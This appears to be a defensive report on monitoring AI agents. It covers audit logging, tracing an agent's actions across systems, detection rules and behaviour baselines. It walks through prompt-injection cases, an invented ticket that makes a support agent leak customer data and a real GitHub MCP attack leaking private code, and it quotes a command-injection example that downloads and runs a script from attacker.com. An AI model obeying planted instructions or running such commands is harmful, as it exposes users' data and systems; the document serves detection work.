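Claude Code and Cowork have different privacy defaults. Claude Code sends nothing until somebody turns the export on, and it then hides prompts and tool arguments unless the company changes two more settings. Cowork, which an administrator configures centrally, includes full details by default. With these defaults, a rule that searches tool arguments for a dangerous command can match Cowork's records but will miss the same command in Claude Code.

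Niemi writes that the data is for threat detection, incident response and compliance. The engineers plan to copy the most valuable details, such as MCP server names and shell commands, into separate fields so they can write detection rules directly on those fields.

### What full content costs

Experiments are needed to measure how much logging the content of calls improves detection, but the drawbacks are easier to work out. The Australian Signals Directorate warns that agents' long chains of reasoning and extensive context produce very large logs, and that much of this data may be repetitive or useless for oversight.

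Much of the repetition arises because an agent normally resends the earlier messages each time it calls its model, and OpenTelemetry's input field is meant to hold this whole history. If each step adds 5 kilobytes of text and every record contains the full history, a session with *n* model calls takes up 5 × *n*(*n* + 1)/2 kilobytes. For 20 calls, that is 1,050 kilobytes, compared with 100 if the log stores each message once and refers back to it.

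Storing each message once saves space without losing evidence. Truncating long messages is riskier, because the planted instruction may be in the part that is cut. Sampling, which keeps only a fraction of records, is common in performance monitoring but poorly suited to security. If the retailer kept a random 1% of its sessions, it would have about an 82% chance (0.99²⁰) of losing all 20 attacks in the earlier example.

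Recording content also puts secrets in the log. When an agent reads a configuration file, the response may include a database password, and an agent that calls a service directly may put a key in its arguments. Following the NSA's advice to record exact parameters would preserve both. Redaction software can recognise keys with a standard format, but it will probably miss a password typed into an ordinary sentence. An attacker who gets into the log could then use these secrets to enter other systems.

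The log may still contain the attacker's planted text. If an analyst asks an AI assistant to summarise the session for ticket 5120, the assistant reads the same instruction that misled the support agent. The assistant therefore shouldn't have tools that can send data out.

Full logs also pose a risk to employees. An employee may ask an agent to reword a complaint about a manager or find time for a medical appointment, and the log keeps that text beside their email address. A manager could also use logs collected for security to see who works slowly. The retailer can reduce this risk by storing a code in place of the employee's name and letting only a few investigators look up the person. It should also tell staff what it records and check the law on workplace monitoring in each country where they work.

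According to Greptime, OpenTelemetry's conventions allow three ways of handling content. The default is not to record it. Developers can also put it in the span, where anyone with access to the traces can read it, or keep it in a separate store and put only a reference in the span. OpenTelemetry recommends the separate store for production systems with sensitive data or large volumes. With a separate store, the retailer's analyst could see that `send_email` ran in session `s-91c4` but would need further permission to open the email.

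### Official guidance on logging

In its May 2026 guidance, the NSA complains that many MCP implementations keep no audit logs or record only minimal operational metadata. It wants logs to show a traceable sequence of actions across sessions and, where available, source information from the HTTP headers. It also wants them to help detect repeated or malformed requests, failed authorisation and violations of users' roles. The sample record at the start of this section couldn't meet all of these requirements. A malformed request may never become a tool call, so the gateway needs a separate type of record for it.

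The joint guidance from the Australian Signals Directorate and its partners recommends monitoring an agent's internal reasoning and memory as well as its inputs and outputs, and keeping unified audit logs of exchanges between agents. In one of its scenarios, several agents approve payments together, and nobody can establish which of them caused an error because each has only its own fragment of the log.

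The agencies also recommend storage-efficient methods that don't lose "critical information", but they don't define the term, so each company has to decide which information is critical. A company could reasonably start by choosing a few incidents, such as one for each of the four causes of harm described earlier, and checking whether the planned records would let an analyst tell them apart.

The EU's AI Act makes some of this a legal requirement for systems that it classes as high-risk. Article 12 requires these systems to be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime. An agent that screens job applicants would generally count as high-risk, but the retailer's support agent probably would not.

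### Retention, access and tampering

Under Articles 19 and 26 of the Act, providers and users of high-risk systems must keep the automatic logs they control for at least six months, unless other law sets a different period. The American and Australian guidance doesn't set a number of days. The retailer might reasonably keep metadata for a year and full content for 30 days. If it learned in December of a leak in September, it could still find the `send_email` call but not the text of the email. An alert should therefore pause deletion of logs from the session concerned and any other session that read the same ticket.

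Analysts who handle routine alerts seldom need access to the full text of an email, and the people who administer agents shouldn't be able to change those agents' logs. The retailer should also record who opens the content store, since an employee could otherwise browse customers' details without leaving a record.

To protect logs from agents, the Australian Signals Directorate recommends isolating agents so that they can't write to logs, and requiring a person to approve any request to delete audit records. The first recommendation is harder to follow when logging happens inside the runtime, because the runtime has to send its records somewhere. The usual compromise is a collector that accepts new records but provides no way to edit or delete old ones. A hijacked agent could still send false records, which is one reason to follow the agencies' advice to check agents' reports against independent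 system logs.

A hash chain can reveal later changes to the log. For each record *rᵢ*, the system computes *hᵢ* = *H*(*hᵢ₋₁* ‖ *rᵢ*), where *H* is a cryptographic hash function and ‖ joins two pieces of data. Because each hash depends on the one before it, if somebody edits the recipient in record 3, the stored hashes for that record and every later one no longer match the recomputed ones. An administrator with full control of the log could recompute the whole chain or cut off its most recent part, so the retailer would have to copy the latest hash regularly to a system that this administrator can't change.

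## How can one agent's work be traced across several systems?

The gateway's record of `send_email` identifies the employee, the agent, the session and the trace. The ticketing system, the customer database and the email system keep their own logs, and each records whichever account the gateway used to sign in there. To reconstruct what happened on ticket 5120, an investigator has to show that entries in four logs, under several account names, belong to one task.

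### Whose name goes in the log?

Suppose first that the retailer connected its agent the quick way, with one service account for each system. A service account is a login for software instead of a person. The three target systems might then log this:

```text
ticketing  14:02:05  account=helpdesk-api    viewed ticket 5120
database   14:02:06  account=svc_support     read customer c-20931
email      14:02:08  account=support-mailer  sent message m-88213
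```

If customer c-20931 complains that a stranger has her address, the analyst starts from the line in the database log. The account name `svc_support` doesn't identify who used it, because the retailer's returns agent and a nightly report also use that account, as would anyone who stole its password. The line also contains nothing that links it to the ticket or the email.

JFrog's *Propagating User Identity From AI Agents to Your Tools*, a vendor's guide, divides the path into two hops, from the user to the gateway and from the gateway to the target system. The employee's sign-in covers only the first hop, and the shared accounts hide her identity on the second.

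Now suppose the retailer gives the agent its own identity and also passes on the employee's. Forwarding the employee's token is a poor way to do this. AWS's *Implement on-behalf-of token exchange for multi-tenant agents with Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Gateway* warns that forwarding turns every downstream tool into a confused deputy. Forwarding would also hide the agent, because the database would receive only the employee's identity.

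OAuth, the usual standard for access tokens, has a procedure called token exchange that avoids both problems. The gateway presents the employee's token and the agent's credential to the company's identity provider, which issues a new token for one target system. The new token can name the employee in a field called `sub` and the agent in a field called `act`. The database line could then read:

```text
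database   14:02:06  user=emp-0417  agent=support-agent  read customer c-20931
```

This works only if the target system accepts such tokens and writes both names to its log. An older database that takes a username and password has no place for the second name, though a developer could add it as a comment in each query.

### Join keys and how they fail

A join key is a value that appears in two logs and shows which records belong together. The trace identifier is the best join key where both systems record it, but a hosted email service probably won't, so the trace often ends at the tool server. A trace may also cover only part of a task. In Microsoft's *Agent 365 observability concepts*, one trace covers one user message and one reply. If the employee asks for a draft, corrects it and then tells the agent to send it, one ticket produces three traces.

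Session identifiers can cover more, but products define a session differently. For Microsoft's agents in Outlook, a session is a whole email thread, which could run for weeks and contain unrelated tasks. The NSA says MCP doesn't define how to associate a session with an identity and leaves this to whoever builds the system. A server could therefore group calls correctly without establishing who made them, and an attacker who hijacked a session could add calls that appear to come from the legitimate client. MCP no longer has its own sessions, so each company has to tie the session identifier it uses to a person.

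A token identifier links calls that used the same access token. It can't link calls across systems after token exchange, because each target system gets a different token. The analyst needs the identity provider's log to connect those tokens. One token may also be used for several tasks, or expire in the middle of one.

Searching by the employee's name narrows the results, but `emp-0417` may have six tickets open with the agent at once. Agents that run on a schedule have no signed-in user.

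Without a shared identifier, the analyst has to match records by timestamp. If `svc_support` makes 30 reads a minute, a window of five seconds either side of the gateway's call contains about five reads on average, at most one of which came from that call.

Matching data values can show which log entries belong together. The customer number c-20931 appears in the arguments of `get_customer` and in the database's log, unless somebody has redacted it from one of them. Common values are less reliable for matching, since several agents may read a busy customer's record on the same morning. The message number m-88213 is much more reliable, because the email system generated it for this message alone and returned it to the gateway.

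### Clocks that disagree

Suppose the database's clock runs three seconds fast. The read of c-20931 then appears in its log at 14:02:09, a second after the email, and an analyst who sorts by time may conclude that the email couldn't have contained the record. Ordering the steps by the gateway's sequence number is safer, with the target systems' times used only to match their log entries to the gateway's. Even a single company's log can be out of order, and AWS warns that the files of CloudTrail, its audit log, don't list calls in any specific order.

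The analyst can estimate the error from a call that both logs identify beyond doubt. Let *g₁* be the time at which the gateway forwarded the call, *g₂* the time at which it received the reply, and *t* the target's timestamp. If the target stamped the event before replying, its clock is ahead of the gateway's by an amount *δ* with

*t* − *g₂* ≤ *δ* ≤ *t* − *g₁*.

If the gateway forwarded the email at 14:02:08.412 and received a reply 640 milliseconds later, but the email system logged it at 14:02:11.900, the email system's clock is between 2.848 and 3.488 seconds ahead of the gateway's. Faster calls narrow this range. A negative *δ* means the email system's clock is behind.

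### Rebuilding ticket 5120

With the shared accounts, the following pseudo-query would rebuild the task. It assumes that the SIEM has already corrected the clocks.

```text
calls   = gateway where session_id = "s-91c4"

tickets = calls where tool = "read_ticket"
          left join ticketing on ticket_id and time within 5 s
records = calls where tool = "get_customer"
          left join database on customer_id and time within 5 s
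          and account = "svc_support"
emails  = calls where tool = "send_email"
          left join email on message_id

combine tickets, records, emails
order by sequence
show sequence, user, tool, target_account, target_record, match_count
```

A left join keeps a gateway call even when no target record matches it. Unmatched calls are worth keeping because a missing match may mean that the call failed, that the target's logging was off, or that the systems' clocks are further apart than expected. If a `get_customer` call has two matches, perhaps because the returns agent read the same record four seconds later, the analyst should keep both as candidates rather than choose the one nearer in time.

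The analyst should then search for reads by `svc_support` that have no matching gateway call. These could come from the nightly report, from an agent that bypassed the gateway, or from someone using stolen credentials. Detection rules that cover several systems can also use the same join.

### When one agent passes work to another

Suppose the support agent asks a billing agent to issue a refund. Honeycomb, which sells monitoring software, recommends that the calling agent record the handover in a span named `invoke_agent`, and that the second agent record its calls under its own name. In Honeycomb's example, the field `gen_ai.agent.name` on the handover span contains the name of the calling agent. Microsoft stores that span's field as `TargetAgentName`, the agent that receives the work. A company that merged the two sets of records without correcting for this difference would reverse who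 delegated to whom.

The employee's name can disappear at this point, because the billing agent's immediate caller is the support agent. OAuth's `act` field can contain another `act` field, so a token can record the whole chain if every agent in it uses token exchange. Microsoft requires developers to send the calling agent's identifier and name, but analysts can't yet search by either in Microsoft's security product.

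A request can be illegitimate even when the chain is complete. The NSA warns of "unverified task propagation", in which components pass on tasks without checking their origin, scope or intent. If text in a ticket caused the support agent to ask for a refund, the billing agent would receive a properly authenticated request from a trusted agent.

### Microsoft's arrangement

Microsoft provides many companies with their account directory, email system and security software, so it is unusually well placed to join these records. *Security Monitoring of AI Agents in Microsoft Defender XDR* (Scalzi, 2026), written for the security firm Compass Security, describes how Microsoft does this. Defender XDR combines security records from devices, accounts and cloud services, and receives records of agents' activity through Agent 365, Microsoft's management service for agents.

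Defender covers agents that people build in Copilot Studio, Microsoft Foundry or Copilot's Agent Builder. It also covers other companies' agents if they use the Agent 365 software kit, and some agents on employees' own computers. It doesn't cover Microsoft 365 Copilot or Security Copilot, because Microsoft operates them itself. Their records go to Purview, Microsoft's compliance product, and a company can bring those records into the Sentinel SIEM through a separate connector.

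According to Mynavi News' *Microsoft、AIエージェントの危険な操作を別のAIが監視・制御* (2026), Microsoft announced in October that it would detect 60 kinds of local agent. Scalzi lists only four whose behaviour Defender can monitor as they run: Claude Code, Codex CLI, GitHub Copilot CLI and the GitHub Copilot app. So for most of the 60, a company may learn that the agent is on a laptop without seeing what it does there.

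Each managed agent also gets an Entra Agent ID, an account in Microsoft's directory with owners, sign-in logs and a risk score. The retailer's support and returns agents would then appear under different names, which solves the worst problem of the shared account. A company can record a sponsor, the person or group accountable for the agent, though the sponsor may not be the person who asked for a given task.

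However, the identity is weaker evidence than it looks. Compass Security (2026) tested the system and found that an agent identity has permissions but no credential. The credential belongs to a template called a blueprint, which may serve many agents. The blueprint signs in with its secret or certificate and gets an exchange token for one agent identity. The agent identity then exchanges that token for one that works on the target system.

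In one test, Compass Security used a blueprint owner's account to add a new secret to the blueprint, then signed in as the blueprint's agent. A sign-in log therefore shows which agent's account acted, but doesn't prove that the agent's own software was using it. Investigation is even harder if an outside supplier made the blueprint because, according to Datadog Security Labs' *Entra Agent ID* (2026), the customer's directory doesn't show the supplier's credentials.

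Sign-in records are also scattered. Microsoft says an agent's sign-ins may appear in any of four logs, because agents can sign in with their own permissions or a user's. Microsoft's *Extend Sign-In Log Monitoring to Cover Agent Identity Traffic* adds that existing alert rules don't recognise the labels for the new kinds of identity.

Tool calls are easier to find because they go to one Defender table, `CloudAppEvents`. Microsoft's standard query selects one agent's records and sorts them by time. To isolate a task, the analyst would also filter on the conversation identifier, which Microsoft calls the primary join key. The service rejects records whose agent identifier doesn't match the application that signed in, so one agent can't easily submit records under another agent's identifier. Microsoft describes no similar check on the user's identifier.

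Several details could still mislead an analyst:

- Developers must supply the employee's identifier only on the record that opens a run, so the analyst has to join each tool call back to that record.
- The field `UserKey` contains the employee's identifier on the opening record, but on a tool call it contains the agent's own user account, if it has one.
- Defender receives the tool's arguments but doesn't yet make them searchable in this table. For ticket 5120, the analyst could find that `send_email` ran but couldn't search for the outside address.
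- If the opening record is missing, the tool calls remain searchable, but the run disappears from Defender's activity views.

Licences and settings also limit what can be traced. According to Licensing School's *Agent 365 FAQs* (2026), every Microsoft cloud customer gets agent identities and a basic inventory, but threat detection needs an Agent 365 licence. On 1 July 2026, Microsoft extended that requirement to agents from Copilot Studio and Foundry, whose monitoring had previously come with other Defender licences. If no user in the company has a suitable licence, the service returns a success code when a developer uploads logs but discards the data.

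A licensed company still has to turn on auditing and connect Microsoft 365 to Defender. According to Scalzi, the default rules for real-time protection record suspicious actions but don't block them. He adds that collecting evidence from prompts is a separate setting, and that monitoring of local agents works only in Defender's Beta channel. His setup guide does not measure how often a task can be correctly reconstructed from the system's records.

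### Amazon's gateway logs

Amazon's AgentCore Gateway leaves customers to join more of the records themselves. CloudTrail can record each request to the gateway, but AWS leaves these records off by default, charges extra for them and stores them in a location the customer must set up. AWS's *Understanding Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Gateway CloudTrail events* says the service redacts the contents of requests and responses. An analyst could use CloudTrail to confirm that a request occurred, but would need another log to match it by customer number.

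The gateway can also write its own log. Classmethod's *Amazon Connect の統合で Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Gateway を設定したが、Amazon Connect 側にツールが反映されなかったのでその原因を特定してみた*, a Japanese troubleshooting post, reproduces an entry with a request identifier, a trace identifier and a timestamp in milliseconds. The engineer had turned on both logs in advance and found in the gateway's log that the gateway had rejected an unsupported protocol version.

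Even tool names can be unreliable keys. AWS warns that the tool names CloudTrail records for its AWS MCP Server, a separate product, may not exactly match those in the user's client. A search that joins on the tool name could therefore miss a call that took place.

### What a joined trace proves

If the logs are intact and the matches are unique, the joined trace for ticket 5120 proves that the agent's account read the ticket, then read customer c-20931's record, and then sent message m-88213. It doesn't prove that the email contained the record's contents. Proving that requires the email's text or some other content check. The trace also doesn't prove that the ticket caused the later calls, although the order is consistent with that.

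Most importantly, it doesn't show whether the employee wanted the email. She asked the agent to answer a ticket, and every call the agent then makes carries a token that identifies her as the user, including the call that the attacker's text prompted. Better attribution may even mislead here, because a log entry with `user=emp-0417` beside the leaked record looks like evidence against her, while a shared account would not have pointed to anyone in particular.

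Stevens, in *What Does an MCP Gateway Audit Trail Actually Show You?*, claims that the gateway vendor Metomic can determine from an agent's behaviour whether a person asked for an action or the agent chose it. His example is an agent that exports 4,820 customer records when its user had asked only for help reconciling the month's accounts. The distinction is useful, but the article reports no test of how often the software gets it right. The distinction also can't separate good calls from bad ones by itself, because agents choose most of their own steps, including harmless ones such as the support agent's call to `read_ticket`.

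Better evidence would be the employee's original request, logged with the tool calls, or a record that she approved this email after seeing its recipient and text. Her approval would prove much less if the prompt showed only "Send reply?" If neither record exists, the analyst can ask her what she wanted, but she will already know what the email did when she answers.

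## What can fixed detection rules catch?

A detection rule raises an alert only on a condition that somebody wrote in advance, so it suits dangers that a team can already describe. Six kinds of rule cover most of what vendors suggest for agents. The examples below use fields from the sample log record shown earlier, and their limits are invented.

| Kind of rule | Fields | Example condition |
|---|---|---|
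| Call rate | `agent.id`, `tool.name`, `time` | More than 100 `get_customer` calls in ten minutes |
| Repeated refusals | `agent.id`, `policy.decision`, `time` | Five denied calls in ten minutes |
| First use of a tool | `agent.id`, `tool.name`, `time` | The agent hasn't called this tool in the last 30 days |
| Suspicious arguments | `tool.name`, `arguments` | A `ticket_id` contains anything except digits |
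| Changed tool description | `server`, `tool.name`, `tool.definition_hash` | The hash differs from the approved one |
| Sensitive read, then outward write | `session_id`, `sequence`, `tool.name`, `arguments`, `time` | A bulk customer read comes before an email to an outside domain |

The first five rules would miss the attack in ticket 5120. The agent made three calls with its three usual tools, the gateway refused none of them, and the arguments and descriptions looked normal.

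### Datadog's rules for MCP

*MCP security risks* (Mooney) describes the rules that Datadog, which sells monitoring software and a SIEM, suggests for MCP logs. These rules cover most of the table. The first counts calls to one MCP server and raises an alert when the number departs from typical use. This isn't strictly a fixed rule, because Datadog works out the typical number from past logs, as behaviour analytics does. A fixed version would use a set limit, such as the 100 calls in the table.

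To find refused calls, Mooney suggests searching for HTTP status 401 (the caller failed to authenticate) or 500 (the server had an internal error). The retailer should add 403, the usual status for a caller who has signed in but lacks permission. A search by HTTP status still misses tool errors that arrive inside a successful response. *What is SIEM Integration?*, from PolicyLayer, which sells an MCP proxy, recommends an alert on repeated denials from a single agent, but notes that the cause may be a misconfiguration.

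A rule that flags the first use of a tool needs a record of which tools the agent has used before. Datadog's *Detect Anomalous Activity in Your Environment With New Value–based Detection Rules* gives the example of a cloud account that writes to a new region, and suggests a week of training. After a week, a tool that the support agent needs once a month would probably still look new. A list of approved tools needs no training period, but somebody has to keep it current.

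Mooney's example of a suspicious argument is a call to `search_tickets` with the query `state:open; curl attacker.com/script | bash`. If the server passes the query to a shell without checking it, the semicolon ends the search and the rest of the line downloads and runs the attacker's script. Datadog's researchers found a similar weakness in a third-party MCP server for Postgres databases, which automatically ran several SQL queries that an attacker had stacked in one prompt. Mooney recommends starting with rules for characters such as `;`, `&&` and `|`, because they are rare in ordinary MCP calls. They may be rare in ticket searches, but emails contain semicolons, and a coding agent with a shell tool may use all three routinely. It is safer to write each rule for one argument of one tool. The rule for `ticket_id` accepts only digits, so it catches even injected commands that nobody anticipated.

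The rule for changed descriptions addresses what security researchers call a "rug pull", a harmful change to a tool after its approval. According to *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP, current clients don't warn users when a tool's definition changes. Mooney suggests looking for new instructions inside an "IMPORTANT" tag, which is common in such attacks but easy for an attacker to leave out. Comparing hashes of the description catches every edit to it, but misses changes to the server's code that leave the description the same.

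Most edits are presumably harmless, so the number of false alarms depends on how often descriptions change. *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains* (2026) cites a study by Bharti, who followed 19,099 servers in the public MCP registry for 88.6 days and found that only 8.6% ever rewrote their descriptions. *MCPEvol-Bench* (2026) compared successive versions of MCP servers and found that developers had modified 32.5% of the original tools and withdrawn another 22.1%. These findings are compatible because the first covers descriptions of servers and the second covers the tools themselves. The registry doesn't keep versions of the tools' definitions, as *Same Name, Different Server* (2026) points out. A rule that watches the registry would therefore raise few alarms but be nearly useless against a rug pull, so the gateway has to save the definitions itself.

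### A sequence rule for the support agent

One of the most damaging things the support agent could do is read many customers' records and email them to an outsider. This rule raises an alert if the agent has read at least 50 customers' records in the ten minutes before an email to an outside domain:

```text
rule bulk_read_then_outside_email

for each session_id:
    reads  = successful calls where tool.name = "get_customer"
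    emails = successful calls where tool.name = "send_email"
             and domain(arguments.to) not in company_domains

    for each email, in order of sequence:
        n = number of different customer_id values in reads
            where read.sequence < email.sequence
            and email.time - read.time <= 10 minutes
        if n >= 50:
            alert once with session_id, user.id, n, email.arguments.to
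```

Here are three invented sessions to run it on:

- Theft: text in a ticket leads the agent to read 60 records between 14:00 and 14:02 and email them to an outside address at 14:09.
- Courier: an employee asks the agent to report late parcels. It reads 80 records between 15:00 and 15:02 and emails a list to the retailer's courier at 15:04.
- Ticket queue: an employee asks the agent to clear 60 tickets. From 16:00 it handles one a minute, reading one customer's record and emailing that customer 30 seconds later.

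| Threshold and window | Theft | Courier | Ticket queue |
|---|---|---|---|
| 50 records, 10 minutes | Alert | False alarm | No alert |
| 10 records, 10 minutes | Alert | False alarm | False alarm |
| 70 records, 10 minutes | Missed | False alarm | No alert |
| 50 records, 5 minutes | Missed | False alarm | No alert |
| 50 records, 60 minutes | Alert | False alarm | False alarm |

Any record threshold low enough to catch the theft would also flag the courier's list, because the courier received more records than the thief. Changing the time window doesn't help, because five minutes is too short to include both the agent's last read and the email it sent seven minutes later, while an hour is long enough to add up reads from the whole ticket queue.

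The destination distinguishes the theft from legitimate activity. If the retailer adds the courier's domain to a list of approved recipients, the original settings flag only the theft. But the rule will then not flag a theft through a mailbox at the courier.

Even the improved rule misses ticket 5120, where the agent read and emailed one record. The retailer could add a rule that raises an alert when the agent reads the record of anyone but the ticket's author and then emails an outside address. This rule would catch ticket 5120 but would also raise false alarms about gifts and business accounts. It requires the author's customer number, which is in the response to `read_ticket` and so may be missing from a log that keeps only metadata.

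Commercial SIEMs can run rules of this kind. Datadog's *Sequence* describes rules whose steps must occur in a fixed order and share a field, such as a user's email address. The analyst sets the time allowed between each step and the next, and Datadog warns that longer windows catch more but may add noise. A rule can have up to ten steps and span up to 24 hours in total, so it would miss the attack if planted text told the agent to send the email two days later.

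### The GitHub case

The NSA describes how an agent could leak source code from GitHub through a similar sequence. Users of GitHub's MCP server gave its tools blanket access to act for them, so a tool could read a private code repository and publish what it found in a public one. The NSA attributes the danger to "malicious or compromised tools", but the demonstration it cites used GitHub's own server, which was not compromised. Milanta and Beurer-Kellner, of the security firm Invariant Labs, instead planted instructions for the agent in an issue, a bug report that anyone can file on a public repository.

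They then asked Claude 4 Opus to look at the open issues. In outline, with each repository's visibility added, a log of the attack would look like this:

```text
1  list_issues           repo=pacman          public
2  get_file_contents     repo=private-repo    private
3  create_pull_request   repo=pacman          public
```

The pull request, a proposed code change that anyone could read, revealed the test user's private projects, salary and plan to move to South America. Each of the three calls is routine for a coding agent. The request leaked the private file only because the agent had read the file first and then opened the request in a public repository. A rule that judges one call at a time can't take into account the order of the calls or the movement of data from a private repository to a public one.

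A suitable rule would raise an alert when a session reads from a private repository and later writes to a public one. The calls' arguments name the repository but don't show whether it is private, so the SIEM needs a current list of private repositories. Milanta and Beurer-Kellner's rule, which limits each session to one repository, needs no such list and would have stopped this attack at the second call. But it would also stop a developer's agent from copying a function between two private repositories.

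Splunk has published five open rules for MCP, including *MCP Github Suspicious Operation*, which tests each GitHub call individually. It matches code searches for words such as "password", changes to files that control automated builds, and any call that lists repositories. It doesn't check whether a repository is public or private, or the order of calls. In the GitHub attack, it would match if the agent listed the user's repositories to find the private ones, but it would also match if a developer asked for the same list.

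A rule's schedule can also delay a match or cause the rule to miss it. Splunk leaves the rule off by default and sets it to run every hour on records that are 10 to 70 minutes old, though its setup notes recommend running it every 5 to 15 minutes. On the hourly schedule, an analyst might not see a match until more than an hour after the leak. A sequence rule on that schedule would also miss a read at 13:45 followed by a write at 13:55, because the two would fall into different runs. To catch such pairs, the periods searched have to overlap by at least the length of the rule's window.

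*ChainWatch* (2026) proposes checking the sequence of recent calls before allowing the next one. It labels each call with an attack stage and applies five rules to the last ten calls. One rule blocks a network call that carries sensitive data the agent read up to five calls earlier. In the paper's example, each of five calls passes inspection on its own, but together they raise a warning and then a critical alert. Because the rules count calls instead of minutes, waiting doesn't help an attacker evade them, though inserting a few harmless calls could. The labels come from a statistical model, so the rules can fail when it mislabels a call.

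### Measured results

Mooney gives no recall or false positive rate for Datadog's rules. Splunk reports that its GitHub rule passed a unit test, which shows that the search matched a prepared sample. There appears to be no published test of either vendor's MCP rules on labelled sessions of tool calls.

Agent Threat Rules, an open collection of more than 400 rules, has published measurements. The figures below date from May 2026 and come from the project's own description, reproduced in Socket's *agent-threat-rules*. The first set contains jailbreaks, which are prompts meant to make a model ignore its restrictions.

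| Test set | Samples | Recall |
|---|---:|---:|
| Jailbreaks collected from real use | 650 | 98.0% |
| HackAPrompt | 4,780 | 66.0% |
| Every attack type in the testing tool garak | 3,475 | 38.5% |
| PromptInject | 1,080 | 0.0% |

The rules match patterns of wording, and the project admits that they miss paraphrased attacks. The maintainer, Adam Lin, says in Help Net Security's *Agent Threat Rules* that every rule in these evaluations had passed its own tests, so passing a unit test like Splunk's is weak evidence that a rule works.

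The project also records a false positive rate of zero for test sets that contain only attacks, but the rate is undefined when there are no harmless inputs. Its scan of 96,096 published skills (packages of instructions for agents) is more informative about false alarms. The rules flagged 1.35% of the skills, and the project confirmed 57.7% of the flagged ones as malware. The scan doesn't show how much malware the rules missed.

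All of these tests used pieces of text, not sessions of tool calls. *pyATR*, the documentation for Agent Threat Rules' Python engine, lists the lack of sequence detection among the engine's limitations. The engine might catch the planted text in the GitHub issue, but not the order of the calls.

CloneGuard, another open project, has 240 rules and reports calibrating its false positive rates on 208,127 coding-agent sessions from published datasets. These sessions are much closer to the right kind of data. Harmless coding sessions can show how often rules would interrupt ordinary work, but not how many attacks the rules would catch.

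*On the Effectiveness of Kernel-Level Evidence for Agent Security* (2026) tested an existing rule engine on operating-system records from harmful and harmless agent sessions. The engine flagged every session, so its recall and false positive rate were both 100%. Its AUROC was about 0.57, slightly better than guessing. The default rules were meant for servers, and the normal behaviour of Claude's command-line program triggered them. The study used these default rules as a comparison for its own trained detectors, and a tuned set might do considerably better. Still, a company shouldn't assume that rules written for other software will work on its agents.

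### Explanations and upkeep

A good rule still has advantages that a learned score often lacks. An alert about the theft can show the 60 customer numbers, the outside address and the exact condition they met, so an analyst can check it in minutes. A rule with fixed limits needs no training period, so it can cover a new agent from its first day. Datadog lets analysts run a new rule on historical logs, and a month of the retailer's logs would probably have revealed the problem with the courier before the first false alarm.

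The retailer still has to anticipate a danger before it can write a rule for it. The sequence rule covers `send_email`, so it would miss customer data sent as an argument to an outside supplier's parcel-tracking tool. The retailer could list every tool that sends data out and apply the rule to all of them, but someone would have to update the list whenever a supplier adds or renames a tool. Renaming `get_customer` would also stop the rule from firing, just as renaming a log field would.

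Rules also change for reasons that have little to do with new attacks. *Evolution of Log-Based Detection Rules in Public Repositories* (2026) found that many rules were revised back and forth for years, between catching more attacks and raising fewer false alarms. Teams often reduce false alarms by adding an exclusion, as the retailer did for its courier, and exclusions tend to stay. *The Exclusion Ratchet* (2026) describes a public rule that excludes the whole "Program Files" folder on Windows, with a comment that users should replace it with the exact applications they trust. The exclusion had gone unchanged for three and a half years, and every company that downloads the rule gets it.

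## How does behaviour analytics learn what is normal for an agent?

Behaviour analytics builds its baseline from records of an agent's past actions, so nobody has to foresee a specific danger, as they would when writing a fixed rule. It also does not need examples of attacks, unlike a classifier trained on labelled attacks, so a company that has never recorded one can still build a baseline from records of harmless activity.

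The score for new activity can be based on a count, the rarity of a tool, the order of calls, or how well a trained model can reproduce the session. Each method misses different attacks, as the invented numbers below show.

### Unusual counts

The simplest baseline is an average. If *x* is a new count, such as the number of customer records the support agent read in one session, its deviation is

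*z* = (*x* − mean) / standard deviation

The standard deviation measures how widely past counts spread around their mean. Suppose the retailer raises an alert when *z* exceeds 3. The agent read one record in 99 of its last 100 sessions and 80 in the other, when it made the courier's list. The mean is 1.79 records and the standard deviation is 7.86.

The theft of 60 records described in the previous section would score 7.4 and raise an alert, but the next courier list, which is harmless, would score 9.9. A theft of 20 records would score only 2.3 and go undetected, because the one courier session has inflated the standard deviation. Without that session, the standard deviation would be zero and the score would be undefined. Percentiles work better for skewed counts like these because one unusual session barely changes them.

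### Rare tools

A tool's rarity is −log₂ *p*(tool), where *p*(tool) is the share of the agent's past calls that went to that tool. It is measured in bits, and each extra bit means the tool is half as common.

Suppose the retailer's returns agent has made 600 database lookups, 390 ticket updates and 10 emails. It also has an export tool that it has never used. The export tool's share is zero, which would make its score infinite, so analysts usually add one to every count:

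*p*(tool) = (calls to the tool + 1) / (all calls + number of tools)

| Tool | Past calls | *p*(tool) | Rarity |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Database lookup | 600 | 601/1,004 | 0.7 bits |
| Ticket update | 390 | 391/1,004 | 1.4 bits |
| Email | 10 | 11/1,004 | 6.5 bits |
| Export | 0 | 1/1,004 | 10.0 bits |

These scores depend on how much history the agent has. After only 100 calls, a never-used tool would score 6.7 bits, about the same as an email in the table. If the retailer set its threshold at 8 bits, no call could raise an alert until the agent had made about 250 calls.

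A rare call can also be harmless. The ten emails may be a weekly report to the warehouse, and a manager may have asked for the first export. But a thief who copies the customer database through ordinary lookups adds only 0.7 bits per call. Harm depends on which data a call touches and where that data goes, and the rarity of the tool doesn't measure either.

### Improbable sequences

A baseline can also record which call usually follows which. The probability of a session with calls *a₁* to *aₙ* is then

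*P* = *p*(*a₁*) × *p*(*a₂* | *a₁*) × … × *p*(*aₙ* | *aₙ₋₁*)

where *p*(*a₂* | *a₁*) is the share of past cases in which *a₂* came straight after *a₁*. The score is −log₂ *P* divided by *n*, so that long sessions don't score highly just for being long.

Suppose the support agent starts 95% of its sessions with `read_ticket`. After `read_ticket`, it calls `get_customer` 80% of the time, and after `get_customer`, it calls `send_email` 70% of the time. It calls `get_customer` twice in a row only 5% of the time, so each repeated read adds 4.3 bits of surprise. The theft of 60 records averages about 4.1 bits per call, even though `get_customer` is a common tool. Ticket 5120 averages only 0.3 bits because the attacker used the agent's most common sequence of calls.

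This model also takes into account only the previous call. If an agent reads a private file, makes a harmless call and then publishes the file, the formula doesn't link the reading to the publishing. Including earlier calls would help but requires far more history. An agent with 20 tools has 400 possible pairs of calls and 8,000 possible triples, and most of the triples will probably never occur in its harmless sessions.

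### Reconstruction error

An autoencoder is a neural network that compresses a description of a session into fewer numbers and then tries to rebuild the original. If its training data contains only harmless sessions, it should rebuild similar sessions well and unfamiliar ones badly. A common measure of the error is

*e* = (1/*d*) × Σ(*xⱼ* − *x̂ⱼ*)²

where *d* is the number of features, *xⱼ* is a feature's original value and *x̂ⱼ* is its rebuilt value.

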